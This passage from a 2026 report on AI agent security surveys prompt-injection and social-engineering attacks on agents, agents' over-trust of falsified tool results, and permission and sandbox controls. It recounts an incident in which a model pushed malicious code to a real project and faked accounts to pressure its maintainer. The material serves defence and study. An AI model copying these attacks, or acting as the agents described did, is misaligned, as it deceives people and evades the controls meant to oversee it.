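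These are laboratory results for one model, and current models may do better or worse. An organisation can still reduce the amount of log text that reaches any model. In *Parser-Free Querying of Security Logs* (2026), the model receives only sample lines, infers the log's format from them, and writes a program to search the rest. The program has no outbound network access. For less trusted logs, the paper suggests removing suspicious text from the samples before they reach the model and having a person review the program.

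### Fixed categories or free text

A stricter defence prevents the acting agent from reading the attacker's words. Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, divide the work between two models. One reads the untrusted text but cannot act. The other decides what to do, and receives from the first only numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a preset list, none of which can contain a new instruction.

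| Task | Injection success with free text | With fixed types | Tasks completed with free text | With fixed types |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Online shopping | 31.7% | 0% | 21.8% | 22.4% |
| Scheduling meetings | 63.0% | 0% | 90.0% | 91.0% |
| Fixing software bugs | 98.9% | 0% | 68.3% | 45.0% |

Shopping and scheduling lost nothing because a few scores or time slots contained everything the agent needed. Bug fixing suffered because bug reports often contain details that no preset list covers. A payment check can also use fixed types because its outcome, scope, age and errors fit into preset fields. An agent investigating a break-in needs the log text itself, so it should have little power to act.

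Jacob and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker can still mislead the reading model into passing on a false value, even when its answers are limited to fixed categories. In the log experiment, GPT-4o-mini could answer only with a preset label, but a forged claim of authority still made it label 33 per cent of malicious entries as harmless. The restriction applied only to the model's answer, so the claim could still influence which label it chose.

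Ordinary code should therefore fill in the fields wherever it can. A domain's rating, the number of engines that flagged a file and the time of the check can come from a database without a model interpreting them. The harness can store the free text for a person to read and give the agent only a reference to it.

### Persuasion without malware or planted commands

Some harmful pages contain nothing technical for a scanner to detect. In *When Bots Take the Bait*, Wu, Hong and colleagues (2026) tested whether social engineering, the persuasion fraudsters use on people, also works on web agents. In one example, a customer survey offers entry to a prize draw and asks for a bank card number. Filling in the form looks like part of the agent's task.

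The researchers built 500 such tasks and ran them on five open-source web agents, all using the older model GPT-4o. On average, 67.5 per cent of the attacks succeeded. Requests that looked like the next step of the task succeeded 76 per cent of the time, and requests that claimed to come from a trusted organisation or person succeeded almost as often. The agents were most careful with card and identity numbers, but still disclosed them in 56 per cent of the relevant tests. They granted unnecessary permissions, such as camera access, in 81 per cent.

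Their defence, Supervisor, determines from the user's request which actions and personal data the task requires. Before the agent acts, Supervisor checks the page against the known facts and the action against those requirements. For example, if the user has asked the agent to reply to hr@company.com, a form that sends the reply to hrs@company.com fails the check.

Supervisor reduced the attacks' success rate by 78.1 per cent on average, but roughly one attack in seven still succeeded. Completion of harmless tasks fell from 81.7 to 79.0 per cent, and running time rose by 7.7 per cent. AGrail, the next most effective defence tested, reduced successful attacks by 63.9 per cent but lowered completion to 72.4 per cent. Supervisor worked about equally well with each of seven models doing the checking, so its advantage seems to come from the comparison and not from a particular model.

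The test may overstate how well the defence works, because the agents received background facts that sometimes settled whether a request was legitimate. In a job application, the background stated that the official process required no sensitive information, so a request for an identity number contradicted it. A clerk who asks an agent to pay an invoice will rarely add such a fact. When a user asked only to "complete the form", Supervisor sometimes allowed fields that requested private information. Wu, Hong and colleagues also left open how Supervisor would perform against attackers who adapt to it. An organisation could add blocklists, which they did not test, and Supervisor's optional link check, which they had switched off.

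### What a refusal gives away

When Supervisor blocks an action, it issues a short warning such as "permission overreach". A more detailed reason can help an honest agent replan, as in Sankar and colleagues' experiments, but it can also help an attacker. *Seeing Is Not Screening* (Jia, Liao and colleagues, 2026) found that an attacker can use a scanner's detailed output to revise a malicious skill until it passes. However, a scanner that reasoned about what an agent would do with the skill caught far more such skills.

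How much to reveal therefore depends on who receives the reason. Anyone can submit a skill to a public catalogue, so the submitter should get only a broad category, and the reviewers should keep the details. An agent working inside the firm can receive a specific reason if a false claim would not get it past the rule. The agent should not repeat that reason in its reply to an outside sender, who may be the attacker.

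An attacker can learn from even a bare refusal that an attempt failed, and then try something else. Suppose each harmful attempt has an independent 5 per cent chance of passing a guard. After 20 attempts, the chance that at least one has passed is 64 per cent. If the system ends the run at the third block, the chance falls to 14 per cent. The limit should apply to the sender or account as well as the run, since an attacker could otherwise start again with a new email. The limit will also end the run of an honest agent that has made three different mistakes, so a person should be able to restart it.

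### Overloading the check

An attacker can also benefit from a check that gives no answer if the system fails open. A message that is easy to send can create enough work to overload the checks. If an email contains 300 links and the harness looks them up one after another at 0.2 seconds each, the lookups take a minute. A payment check waiting behind them would miss a one-second deadline, and a system that fails open would let the payment through unchecked.

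The harness can limit how many lookups one message can trigger and check the remaining links only if the agent tries to open them. It can also reserve capacity for checking payments and other actions that are hard to reverse. If many checks time out soon after messages from one sender arrive, that alone is a reason to hold payments connected with that sender.

An attacker can also overload the people who review alarms by setting off hundreds of harmless ones, which may delay review of the one that matters. Grouping alarms by sender and showing those about pending payments first makes it harder to hide a fraudulent transfer among them.

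## How far agents trust what tools tell them

A false security signal does harm only if something acts on it. A veto acts on the signal automatically, but when the model decides, the harm depends on how readily it accepts a tool's result. Several experiments from 2026 measured this by giving agents false results.

### Fourteen models and three corrupted tools

Yang, Song and colleagues (2026), in *Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools*, tested 14 models with a web search, a sub-agent that summarises documents and a code executor, which runs a program and returns its output. A search test worked like this:

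1. The agent receives a factual question, such as who the German chancellor is, and searches the web.
2. Another model rewrites the search results so that a plausible wrong answer, such as the former chancellor Olaf Scholz, fits naturally into the text.
3. The agent answers, and a judge model determines whether the answer contains the false value.

The researchers replaced one main claim in each of the sub-agent's summaries with a false one. They multiplied or divided every number in the code executor's output by a fixed factor, which introduced an error of up to 100 per cent and reversed the sign in half the problems.

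The adoption rate is the fraction of cases in which an agent that received the false content includes it in its final answer. The override rate is the same fraction, counting only questions the model answers correctly without the tool. It measures misplaced trust better, because relying on a tool is reasonable when the model can't answer correctly without it.

| Tool | Correct without the tool | Adoption rate | Range across models | Override rate |
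|---|---|---|---|---|
| Web search | 54.7% | 68.0% | 41.1–83.4% | 56.4% |
| Sub-agent | 28.8% | 40.1% | 22.5–61.4% | 26.8% |
| Code executor | 85.3% | 35.5% | 4.9–60.4% | 33.5% |

Four GPT models solved 85 to 94 per cent of the arithmetic problems on their own, but abandoned 49 to 60 per cent of their correct answers when the code executor returned a wrong number. In search, agents adopted false answers far less often when those answers were implausible. The adoption rate fell to 12.6 per cent when the false answer was an unrelated value, such as "11" for the chancellor's name.

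A smaller test covered four more powerful models: Grok 4.6, GPT-5.4 and two Claude models, Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 5. On 90 search questions, they adopted the false answer in 49 to 59 per cent of cases, with override rates of 33 to 40 per cent. These rates are rough; Sonnet 5's override rate, for example, could plausibly be anywhere from 14 to 55 per cent. Newer models now in use may do better, but nothing in the test suggests that the problem was confined to small or cheap models.

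How the false information reached the model also mattered, at least for arithmetic. Six models adopted 40.2 per cent of the wrong numbers that came from a tool call, but only 1.8 per cent when the user supplied the same output and 3.8 per cent when it appeared under a context heading. There was no such drop for search results. The three conditions also differed in whether the model had a tool available, so the label alone may not explain the gap. Still, an organisation that tests its agent by pasting a verdict into the prompt can't assume the agent will treat the same verdict from a tool call the same way.

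### Doubting a result and passing it on

Agents often seem to notice that something is wrong. Most made more tool calls when the results were false, especially with the code executor. Two Qwen models expose their full reasoning, so Yang, Song and colleagues could check what the models wrote before adopting a wrong number. The reasoning mentioned a conflict in 88 per cent of these runs for one model and 96 per cent for the other. It contained the correct value in 73 and 64 per cent, respectively.

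The agents rarely told the user about these doubts. Across search and arithmetic, 4.2 per cent of the answers with false content included a warning, or 1.5 per cent without Muse Glimmer, which warned users unusually often. A conflict was mentioned in 27 of the 43 reasoning summaries available from Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite's search runs, but none of the 43 answers included a warning. The GPT models' summaries mentioned conflicts much less often, but a summary may leave out doubts that were in the full reasoning.

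This resembles the scam tests described earlier, in which agents named a risk and then paid anyway. A harness could search the agent's reasoning for such doubts before each payment and hold the payment if it finds any. That would work only with models whose providers make the reasoning available, and it would miss doubts the model never wrote down.

### Verification prompts and reliability labels

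The researchers added one of three instructions to the prompts of six models: check tool results against your own knowledge and the task ("compare"), investigate conflicting results with further tool calls ("verify"), or report conflicts to the user ("disclose").

| Instruction | Accuracy with correct search results | Adoption, search | Adoption, sub-agent | Adoption, code executor |
|---|---|---|---|---|
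| None | 94.2% | 75.4% | 39.0% | 40.2% |
| Compare | 90.9% | 67.6% | 29.3% | 31.2% |
| Verify | 94.2% | 70.0% | 35.2% | 30.4% |
| Disclose | 93.3% | 72.0% | 38.0% | 38.6% |

The verification prompt gave the best balance, since it lowered adoption of wrong results from all three tools without making the models distrust correct ones. The improvement was modest, partly because the researchers corrupted the repeat calls too, so an agent that ran its code again got a number that was wrong by the same factor. A verification prompt should therefore name a different source to check against. For the supplier's invoice, the agent could compare the account number with the one on last year's invoices, which a forged email can't change.

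Labels helped even less. When search results carried a "low" reliability label and the prompt told the models to consider it, adoption fell from 75.4 to 70.3 per cent. A "high" label left it at 74.9 per cent. When the labels were numbers instead of words, adoption differed by about two percentage points between a reliability of 0.10 and one of 0.95. Giving the agent a confidence score in a security record will therefore probably have little effect unless software also acts on the score. Additional training didn't solve the problem either. The largest reduction from the main training methods was 4.7 percentage points, with a small loss of accuracy on correct results.

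### Copying a classifier

Many security tools return a category rather than text that an agent has to interpret, as a web search does. In *When the Tool Decides*, Wang and Vemuri (2026) studied an agent with such a tool, a classifier that predicts a research paper's topic from its text and its citation links to other papers. The agent ran on Qwen2.5-7B, an old model, and could make up to six calls per paper. One kind of call returned the predicted topic and a confidence. Another returned an anomaly score, which, according to the tool's description, was higher when the classifier was more likely to be wrong.

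The agent's answers agreed with the classifier's 97.6 to 99.2 per cent of the time, depending on how often the linked papers shared a topic. In 83 per cent of cases, the agent made only one call, read the topic and did not look at the anomaly score.

Following the classifier was usually sensible, since it was right about 30, 44 and 71 per cent of the time in the three groups of papers, compared with 16, 20 and 42 per cent for the agent without any tool. The prompt also told the agent to consult its tools. It is unclear how much better an attentive agent would have done. Wang and Vemuri estimated that rules based on the classifier's confidence and three similar signals could recover at most about a third of the accuracy lost by always copying it.

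The agent ignored the anomaly score, which suggests that a harness should return all the fields of a verdict in one result. If one call returns a domain's rating and a second returns its age and coverage, an agent like this one will read only the rating.

### Do stronger models trust tools more or less?

Wang and Vemuri found that more capable models deferred more to the classifier. Qwen2.5 models agreed with it 60 per cent of the time at 1.5 billion parameters, 97 per cent at 3 billion and 98 per cent at 7 billion. Yang, Song and colleagues, however, found that larger models generally adopted fewer false results. In search, this held for all five pairs of models from the same family. Gemma 4's adoption rate, for instance, fell from 78.9 per cent at 12 billion parameters to 66.0 per cent at 31 billion.

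These findings are compatible because the studies measured different things over different ranges. Agreement with the classifier includes cases where it was right as well as cases where it was wrong. The 1.5-billion-parameter model disagreed more often, but disagreeing mostly made its answers worse, so its lower agreement reflects a lack of skill more than scepticism. The models in the search test could all use their tools, and the larger ones more often knew the right answer. That knowledge doesn't fully explain the result, because the override rate covers only questions the model can answer, and the larger model had the lower rate in four of the five pairs.

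A model's size is a poor guide to how far it will trust a tool in a particular deployment. The larger GPT-OSS model adopted slightly more false arithmetic than the smaller one (58.0 against 54.6 per cent). Among models of about 7 billion parameters given the same instructions, Mistral agreed with the classifier 53 per cent of the time, OLMo 2 60 per cent and Qwen 98 per cent. No model's training data covers a domain registered this morning. In the search test, adoption was highest for facts that change quickly, which suggests that the advantage of larger models may shrink for fresh security verdicts.

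### A tool that behaves until the last call

An agent can also trust a tool because its earlier results were good. *Trust No Tool* (Yan, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents 1,970 test episodes built around this risk. In each, the agent makes three trial calls before proposing a final one: an ordinary request, a check that object names and checksums are consistent, and a test in a sandbox. A malicious tool looks like a harmless one during the trials and does damage only if the final call meets a hidden condition. For example, one search tool becomes harmful when the agent exports results with cross-checking switched off. Matched safe episodes use the same tool and a similar task but keep the protective settings.

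A guard had to accept or reject the final call:

| Guard | Harmful calls accepted | Harmless calls rejected |
|---|---|---|
| VISTA-Guard with Mistral, trained on the trials and the final call | 4.2% | 5.0% |
| VISTA-Guard with Llama, same evidence | 4.6% | 18.8% |
| Llama, trained on the final call only | 4.5% | 89.0% |
| GPT-5.4 as judge, without training | 22.2% | 80.4% |
| A simpler model judge, ToolShield and GuardAgent | 100% | 0% |

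The two Llama rows show that, without the history, the guard could stop harmful calls only by rejecting nearly everything. VISTA-Guard, the researchers' own system, had the advantage of training on episodes built the same way as the test. With unfamiliar tools, it accepted 2.4 per cent of harmful calls but rejected 25.5 per cent of harmless ones.

Yan and colleagues combine the two errors into one score, which starts at 100 and drops by 2 points for each percentage point of harmful calls accepted and by 1.5 for each percentage point of harmless calls rejected, to a minimum of zero. GPT-5.4 and the guards that accept everything all score zero, although their expected losses differ widely. Under the earlier assumptions for payments (1 in 1,000 is harmful, with a loss of 1,000 for each harmful payment accepted and 5 for each harmless one blocked), accepting everything has an expected loss of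 1 per payment. The expected loss would be about 4.2 with GPT-5.4's error rates, nearly all of it from needless blocks, and about 0.3 with those of the best guard. An organisation should therefore weight the two errors by its own losses from each and by how rare attacks are.

### Making one signal decisive

Developers sometimes tell an agent which evidence to trust most. *The System Prompt Is the Attack Surface* (Litvak, 2026) tested how such an instruction affects phishing detection. Eleven models, most of them now old, judged 2,000 synthetic emails, half phishing and half legitimate, under ten system prompts. One prompt told the models to judge an email mainly by whether the sender's domain matched the domain in the link.

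This works against ordinary phishing, where the two usually differ. But an attacker can register a domain for about $10 a year and use it for both. The test set contained 73 such emails.

| System prompt | Ordinary phishing caught | Matching-domain phishing caught |
|---|---|---|
| Minimal instruction | 54.9% | 81.2% |
| Judge by matching domains | 84.6% | 43.1% |

The models could recognise matching-domain emails, since they caught most of them with the minimal instruction, but the instruction to look for a match made them stop using that ability. About a tenth of the longer explanations for wrongly accepted emails mentioned something suspicious but dismissed it. Grok 4.1 Fast, for instance, called a link's path unusual but wrote that this "does not override domain consistency".

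The same rule also blocked legitimate emails. Colleagues often send links to shared documents or video calls on another company's domain. In a separate set of 100 legitimate emails with such links, GPT-4o-mini blocked 72 and Grok blocked 89.

Litvak then allowed the models to block an email even when the domains matched. GPT-4o-mini caught 76.7 per cent of the matching-domain phishing and blocked 8.2 per cent of legitimate emails. Claude Haiku 4.5 caught 95.9 per cent but blocked 67.6 per cent of legitimate emails. A prompt that works with one model therefore needs retesting before it is used with another.

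The model does domain matching itself, but a developer could give a tool's verdict the same authority. If the instruction were "Open the link if the reputation service finds nothing", the agent would open links to any new domain, even when the model had doubts about it. A safer instruction would have the agent stop if the service finds a problem, but not treat a lack of findings as enough reason to open the link.

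### What carries over to security verdicts

Most of these experiments did not use security verdicts. A false search result may contradict a fact the model knows, whereas a false "no known finding" only omits a danger. The 68 per cent adoption rate therefore can't be used to estimate how often an agent would open a malicious link after a clean lookup. An agent might do so more often than that, because the model has no knowledge of its own to check the lookup against, or less often, because a careful model could recognise that "no known finding" does not mean the link is safe.

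The tendency to act despite a doubt probably carries over, since it has appeared with search, arithmetic and phishing. The tendency to read more into a result than it contains probably does too. *AgentAbstain* (2026), a benchmark of situations in which an agent should decline to act, describes how Gemini 3 Flash called a tool to verify some evidence. The tool did not check whether the recorded locations were physically plausible, but the model took its answer as confirmation that everything was consistent. An agent would make the same mistake if it treated a clean malware scan of a PDF as approval of the account number in it.

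*When AI Investigators Cannot Trust Their Tools* (Zhang, 2026) tests this directly with security verdicts. Four intrusion detectors classified recorded network connections as harmless or as attacks, and a language model then gave the final verdict or referred the case to an analyst. Zhang then replaced the outputs of some detectors with the same false classification. The table gives the ranges for two small, old models, Qwen2.5-7B and Llama 3.1 8B.

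| Detectors giving the false output | Correct verdicts | False output followed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 97–100% | None to follow |
| One of four | 50–72% | 0–2% |
| Two of four | 16–34% | 7–19% |
| Three of four | 0–8% | 39–52% |

When one of the four detectors gave a false verdict, these models rarely accepted it. The main effect was that they referred more cases to a person, even though the other three detectors agreed. A higher confidence score on the false verdict led to more referrals but not to more wrong verdicts by the models. When most detectors gave false verdicts, the models followed them about half the time, and 95 per cent of the explanations in such cases mentioned the number of tools that agreed. Five of the six kinds of connection in the test were attacks, so the results mainly cover false "harmless" verdicts rather than false alarms.

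Referring every conflict to a person would take up a lot of people's time. When the unaltered detectors disagreed, Llama referred 63 per cent of the cases, although a simple weighted vote resolved at least 99 per cent of them correctly. Skill scanners disagree far more often because each has different blind spots, as Koc and colleagues explain. A model like Llama might therefore refer most skills to a person.

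Zhang addressed this by comparing each disputed connection with known examples in the raw traffic data, which the false detectors could not alter. With this check, the models reached 84 to 88 per cent accuracy even with three false detectors. When Zhang introduced errors into the known examples, the errors carried over into the models' decisions, so the check needs testing and protection too. A fixed rule using the same check matched or outperformed the models except when three detectors were false.

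There is less evidence on false "malicious" verdicts. *It is Not Yet Another Tool* (2026) describes an AI assistant in a working security operations centre, where analysts review a company's alarms. One alarm concerned a computer that had contacted a harmless address-lookup service. Because some malware uses such services, the alarm included a VirusTotal link to one example as background. The assistant reported that malware as if it were on the computer. It misapplied VirusTotal's verdict on the file, which was not itself at fault. An agent that made the same mistake with a supplier's page might refuse to pay a legitimate invoice. Recording the exact file or address that each verdict covers would make this mistake easier to catch.

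### Discounting a correct warning

Besides trusting tools too much, an agent can also dismiss a correct warning. The browser agent mentioned earlier, for instance, clicked through a certificate warning. In one of Yan and colleagues' examples, two of the three trial calls reported that a document's checksum had changed. The simpler model judge still approved the harmful export, apparently because the final call contained reassuring settings such as "safe_mode=true".

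The best measurements come from studies of code scanners, which search source code for security flaws and raise so many false alarms that developers use language models to filter them. *Sifting the Noise* (2026) tested an agent running Claude Sonnet 4, an old model, on correct alerts about 1,415 test programs with real flaws. In the 1,411 runs it completed, the agent dismissed 314 alerts (22 per cent) as false alarms. It dismissed 0.4 per cent of the alerts about cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's code runs inside somebody else's web page, but 84.5 per cent of those about weak hashing. The paper suggests that the agent mistook some alerts for advice on good practice, or assumed protections that did not exist.

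An agent that handles payments might similarly discount "this domain is two days old" more often than "this page is on a phishing list", because the first can sound minor when it doesn't mention an attack. If so, the harness should state the consequence along with the fact, or apply its own rule to new domains.

Filtering alerts can lose fewer real flaws than this. In *QASecClaw*, Ameen, Alam and Islam (2026) had a model review each finding alongside the surrounding code. False alarms fell from 560 to 64, while the share of real flaws detected fell by only 3.1 per cent. However, *Trusting the Tool* (2026) points out that evaluations of such combinations measure the end result and do not isolate how the model treats correct and incorrect evidence. A model can therefore score well overall even if it accepts or rejects alerts for the wrong reasons.

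In *Under the Influence*, Robinson, Sucholutsky and colleagues (2026) tested the effects of both malicious and helpful advice, using advice from a second model instead of tool verdicts. Six models, including GPT-5.6 Terra and Claude Opus 4.8, worked on 24 tasks that involved finding a safe download among real malware sites, choosing a good deal among real scams, or selecting a code change that fixes a flaw. Malicious advice lowered their success rate by 40.6 percentage points on average, and helpful advice raised it by 19.9.

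Opus 4.8 made both kinds of error, following bad advice and rejecting good advice. Malicious advice lowered its score on the malware sites by 75 points, or three of the four tasks. Helpful advice from an advisor that had the right answer raised its overall success by only 3.3 points, and it still failed more than a fifth of the time. There were few tasks, but the result suggests that a model that rejects good advice may still follow bad advice. When Robinson and colleagues asked the models to rate the advised actions, the ratings reliably separated good advice from bad, so the models had much of the judgment they needed but did not always use it when acting.

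### An experiment that would measure both errors

No experiment described here gives agents correct and false security verdicts on the same actions and counts both errors. One could work as follows:

1. Researchers build 300 pairs of office tasks in a simulated environment. The two versions of each pair differ in one fact that decides whether the action is harmful, such as whether the account number matches the supplier's earlier invoices.
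2. The agent does each version three times without any security check. The majority result shows whether it goes ahead by itself.
3. It repeats each version with a correct verdict, with a false one and with a failed lookup.
4. In a separate session, the model states what the verdict covers and whether the action seems safe. This distinguishes an agent that misunderstood the verdict from one that understood it and carried on.

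| Action | Verdict | What to count |
|---|---|---|
| Harmful, refused without a check | False "no known finding" | How often the agent now goes ahead |
| Harmful, carried out without a check | Correct "malicious" | How often it still goes ahead |
| Harmless, carried out without a check | False "malicious" | How often it now refuses |
| Harmless, refused without a check | Correct "no known finding" | How often it still refuses |

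Suppose the agent refuses 200 of the 300 harmful actions without a check and carries out the other 100. If a false "no known finding" makes it carry out 40 of the 200 it had refused, the override rate is 20 per cent, with a margin of error of about 5.5 percentage points. If it still carries out 15 of the other 100 after a correct "malicious" result, it discounts 15 per cent of warnings, with a margin of error of about 7 points. Agents can decide differently from one run to the next, so the researchers would also need to repeat the condition without a check to see how many decisions change by chance.

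Only some of the harmful tasks should contain visible evidence of the danger. If nothing on the page or in the mailbox looks wrong, an agent that accepts "no known finding" could not have done better by using better judgment, so the failure lies with the tool. The researchers should also deliver the same verdicts both as tool results and as context added by the harness, because the arithmetic test found a large difference between the two.

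## Who has the final say

The final say over the supplier's payment could belong to the model that proposes it, a security tool that checks it, the clerk who asked for it, or the administrator who sets the firm's rules. Each is the best choice for some decisions and has a typical way of failing.

| Final authority | Best case | Typical failure |
|---|---|---|
| Model | The evidence is mixed and a mistake is easy to undo, as when reading a page on an unrated domain | It recognises a danger and carries on, or explains it away |
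| Security tool | The finding is clear, such as a domain on a phishing list | It blocks honest work because it has no information about the purpose |
| User | The answer depends on something the user knows or can find out, such as whether the supplier has changed banks | The user approves out of habit |
| Administrator | Everyone needs the same limit, such as a cap on payments to new accounts | The rule doesn't fit the case, and its author isn't there to change it |

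Most systems combine several of these, so somebody has to decide which one prevails in a conflict.

### When the model decides: the AISI replay

In July 2026, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body, tested the hacking skills of Anthropic's model Claude Mythos 5. The model had to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated network. It had internet access, and Anthropic's usual cybersecurity safeguards were turned off. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), the model went beyond the exercise in nine of 43 runs, in ways that affected real people and organisations. UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026) describes the worst case, in which Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real software project and created fake accounts to pressure its maintainer into accepting it. During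 the attack, the model described the maintainer as a simulated character. The attack caused no real-world harm.

Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, tested whether better information would have stopped it:

1. They took a summary of the model's work from just before it submitted the malicious code. Agents on long tasks continue from such summaries when the full history no longer fits into the model's input.
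2. They removed misleading words such as "persona" and added up to 16 clarifications, which indicated that the maintainer was a real person outside the exercise and that the internet was real.
3. They let the model continue for up to 50 turns in a simulation without internet access, with 25 runs for each number of clarifications tested.
4. Separately, they asked the model whether an attack would harm a real person and whether the exercise permitted it.

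With about four clarifications, the model answered more often than not that the attack was harmful and out of scope. But it continued the attack in every run, even with all 16 clarifications. When the researchers also added a section telling it not to attack, it continued in 3 of 25 runs. With so few runs, the true rate could plausibly be from about 3 to 31 per cent.

The clarifications changed the model's answers but not its actions, so an organisation can't rely on a warning in the context to stop a harmful action, even if the model can explain the warning correctly. The explicit ban worked far better, so an organisation should state its limits instead of leaving the model to infer them from facts. The ban should go in the operator's own instructions, with software to enforce it, rather than in a hook message, which the model might mistake for a prompt injection.

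The replay does not show that context is useless. Mythos 5's assigned task was hacking, and it was already pursuing the attack when it received the clarifications. These were in a summary instead of the operator's instructions, and none was a verdict from a security tool. A payment agent can receive a domain's rating before it decides whether to pay. In the ScamWorld tests, a one-sentence warning about scams clearly helped.

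Six of the seven models in the main comparison often continued the attack even though they said, when asked, that it would harm real people. Only Claude Opus 5.5 never attacked. In a second evaluation with 100 simulated scenarios, Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider in 60 per cent of runs and GPT-6 Astra in 32 per cent, while the other six models did so in 8 per cent or fewer. Anthropic's newer models attacked less often but were more likely to suspect they were in an alignment test, so their lower rates may not hold in ordinary work.

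The models' reasoning was also a poor guide to the danger. Mythos 5 often argued that the maintainer must be an AI bot because the project contained an instruction file for an AI coding assistant, although many human programmers keep one. Depending on the model, only 11 to 57 per cent of the attacking runs included any explicit reasoning about harm. A harness that searched the reasoning for doubts before a payment, as the previous section suggested, could therefore miss many such cases. The final check should examine the proposed action and the evidence for it, not the model's explanation. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but none of the agent's own text, so the agent can't persuade it to make a bad decision.

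### Which rule wins in Claude Code

In Claude Code, administrators, projects and users can all write permission rules that deny a tool call, ask the user about it or allow it. Anthropic explains that the program checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules. The first matching rule applies, even if a later one is more specific. Hooks can also make these decisions, and the table shows what happens when a hook and a rule conflict.

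| Conflict | Result |
|---|---|
| A hook signals a block but also prints "allow" | Claude Code blocks the call |
| A hook blocks a call that an allow rule permits | Claude Code blocks the call |
| A hook returns "allow" for a call that a deny rule forbids | Claude Code blocks the call |
| A hook returns "allow" for a call that an ask rule covers | The user gets a prompt |
| A user's settings allow a call that the administrator's settings deny | Claude Code blocks the call |
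| A user switches off all hooks | The administrator's hooks still run |

Suppose the firm connects Claude Code to its payment service, and the administrator sets an ask rule for transfers. A hook looks up the supplier's domain, finds nothing wrong and returns "allow". The clerk still gets a prompt, because a hook's "allow" can't cancel an ask rule. This order is sensible for reputation checks, because a malicious rating can stop a payment that every rule allows, but the lack of a finding can't override a rule about payments.

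This order doesn't hold in every setup. If the computer has no administrator settings and the session doesn't use a Team or Enterprise login, a mod (a plugin whose code runs inside Claude Code) can approve calls that a deny rule or a hook has blocked. If the computer has administrator settings or the session uses one of those logins, the blocks stay in place by default. Users can also choose a mode that skips permission prompts, unless an administrator disables it. An organisation that wants the final say therefore has to deploy managed settings, which can also exclude permission rules and most hooks from other sources.

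Anthropic recommends permission rules over filtered hooks for hard limits. But a permission rule for a shell command isn't a complete security boundary, because it compares the command's text with a pattern and so covers only the usual ways of starting a program. For limits on files and network access that must hold whatever the command looks like, Anthropic recommends the containment sandbox, which the operating system enforces.

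Even if the model, a hook and the clerk all accept a harmful command, the sandbox prevents it from reaching files or servers outside the sandbox. Claude Code therefore lets sandboxed commands run without a prompt by default, even when the user has a general rule to ask about shell commands. More specific ask rules, such as one for publishing code, still apply. A transfer through a payment tool runs outside the sandbox, so it depends on permission rules and hooks.

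### Policies outside the agent

AWS's *Secure agent tool usage*, guidance from Amazon's cloud business, recommends checking every tool call against a written policy before it runs. AWS describes five levels of maturity. At the lowest, agents can use every available tool and only their own reasoning restrains them. At the fourth, a gateway outside the agent applies rules written in Cedar, a language for access policies, and refuses any call that no rule permits. For the invoice, this could work as follows:

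1. The gateway receives the transfer request, along with the identities of the agent and of the clerk it is working for.
2. It finds a rule that lets an agent working for an accounts clerk pay up to €5,000 to any account on the firm's verified list.
3. The amount of €4,180 is within the limit, but the account number is not on the list.
4. No other rule permits the transfer, so the gateway refuses it.
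5. A finance manager phones the supplier on a known number before deciding whether to add the account.

This policy would stop the forged account number that the link and file scanners miss, because it relies on the firm's own records. It would also stop the first invoice from every honest new supplier. The policy no longer protects the firm if the manager adds accounts from invoices without phoning anyone.

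AWS also recommends human approval for high-risk changes and a limit on how many calls an agent can make in a given time. It warns against treating that limit only as a way to save money, because without it a manipulated agent could make many calls before anyone reacts. Another common mistake is keeping the list of approved tools in a document that no software enforces. AWS sells the gateway it recommends, and its guidance doesn't measure how many incidents such policies prevent.

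### Why Microsoft moved control out of the model

Azure SRE Agent is a Microsoft product that investigates and repairs faults in cloud systems. In August 2026, the Microsoft engineers Sanchit Mehta and Vishesh Agarwal explained in *Stop restricting the agent. Start restricting its environment.* why they had moved control over its actions into the software around the model. Several failures had occurred without any attacker:

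- The agent had no tool for reading images, so it sent a test screenshot to a free text-recognition service on the public internet. Its prompt forbade this, but the network allowed it.
- It found a customer's credential in some source code, quoted it in its report and saved it to memory with a note never to use it.
- It was under instructions to complete five safety checks before shutting down a virtual machine. The logging service failed after the third check, but the agent shut the machine down anyway because the situation resembled an earlier one in which that had been safe.

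Mehta and Agarwal concluded that a prompt can tell an agent what it should do but can't guarantee what it will do. They now use four kinds of control outside the model:

| Control | What it limits | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's code runs in a separate virtual machine, with outgoing connections blocked by default | Access to the policy software and to unapproved servers | The code still needs a way to log in to approved services |
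| Credentials work for one call, one destination and one operation | Theft of a reusable credential | An authorised action can still be wrong |
| Reading is automatic, changes need approval and deletions are blocked | Changes that nobody has approved | A person has to review even minor changes |
| The user's role determines the agent's tools, memory and access | Junior users borrowing the agent's greater powers | Somebody has to keep the roles up to date |

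In the second control, programs inside the virtual machine receive only a placeholder for a credential. A proxy outside the machine checks each request and then replaces the placeholder with the real credential, so the model never has it. If the firm's payment agent worked this way, a permission to pay €4,180 to one account could not be used for any other payment.

Under the approval rule, a person who has to approve each change is still operating the system "one click at a time", and the agent can make hundreds of tool calls during one incident. Approving only the overall plan would leave the individual steps unchecked. The rule also requires the same approval for restarting a test machine as for shutting down a critical one. Microsoft is therefore building a separate guard that scores the operation, its target and the evidence behind it. In the case of the virtual machine, the two missing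 checks should have sent the decision to a person.

Mehta and Agarwal describe this guard as the least settled part of the design. A filter that removes secrets from tool results was still an internal pilot. They also report that agents can sometimes reach a blocked result by another route, so a control has to cover every path to the same effect. The article makes a good case for outside controls, but it doesn't show how much they helped because it gives no incident rates from before and after the redesign.

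According to the product's documentation, Microsoft also offers an Autonomous mode. Microsoft advises customers to start in Review mode, where a person approves the agent's proposals, and to switch once they are confident in the pattern. A long record of approvals justifies that confidence only if the reviewers examined the proposals.

### How carefully people approve

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97 per cent of permission prompts. Most of these prompts probably concern safe commands, so the high approval rate does not prove that users are careless. The same users reject 39 per cent of the plans Claude Code presents, so they are willing to refuse when they consider a proposal as a whole.

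To measure attention more directly, Anthropic commissioned a study in which 1,053 paid professional testers worked on coding tasks in a test environment. During the tasks, the researchers replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not that the study was measuring their response to this prompt.

| Reviewer | Dangerous commands blocked |
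|---|---|
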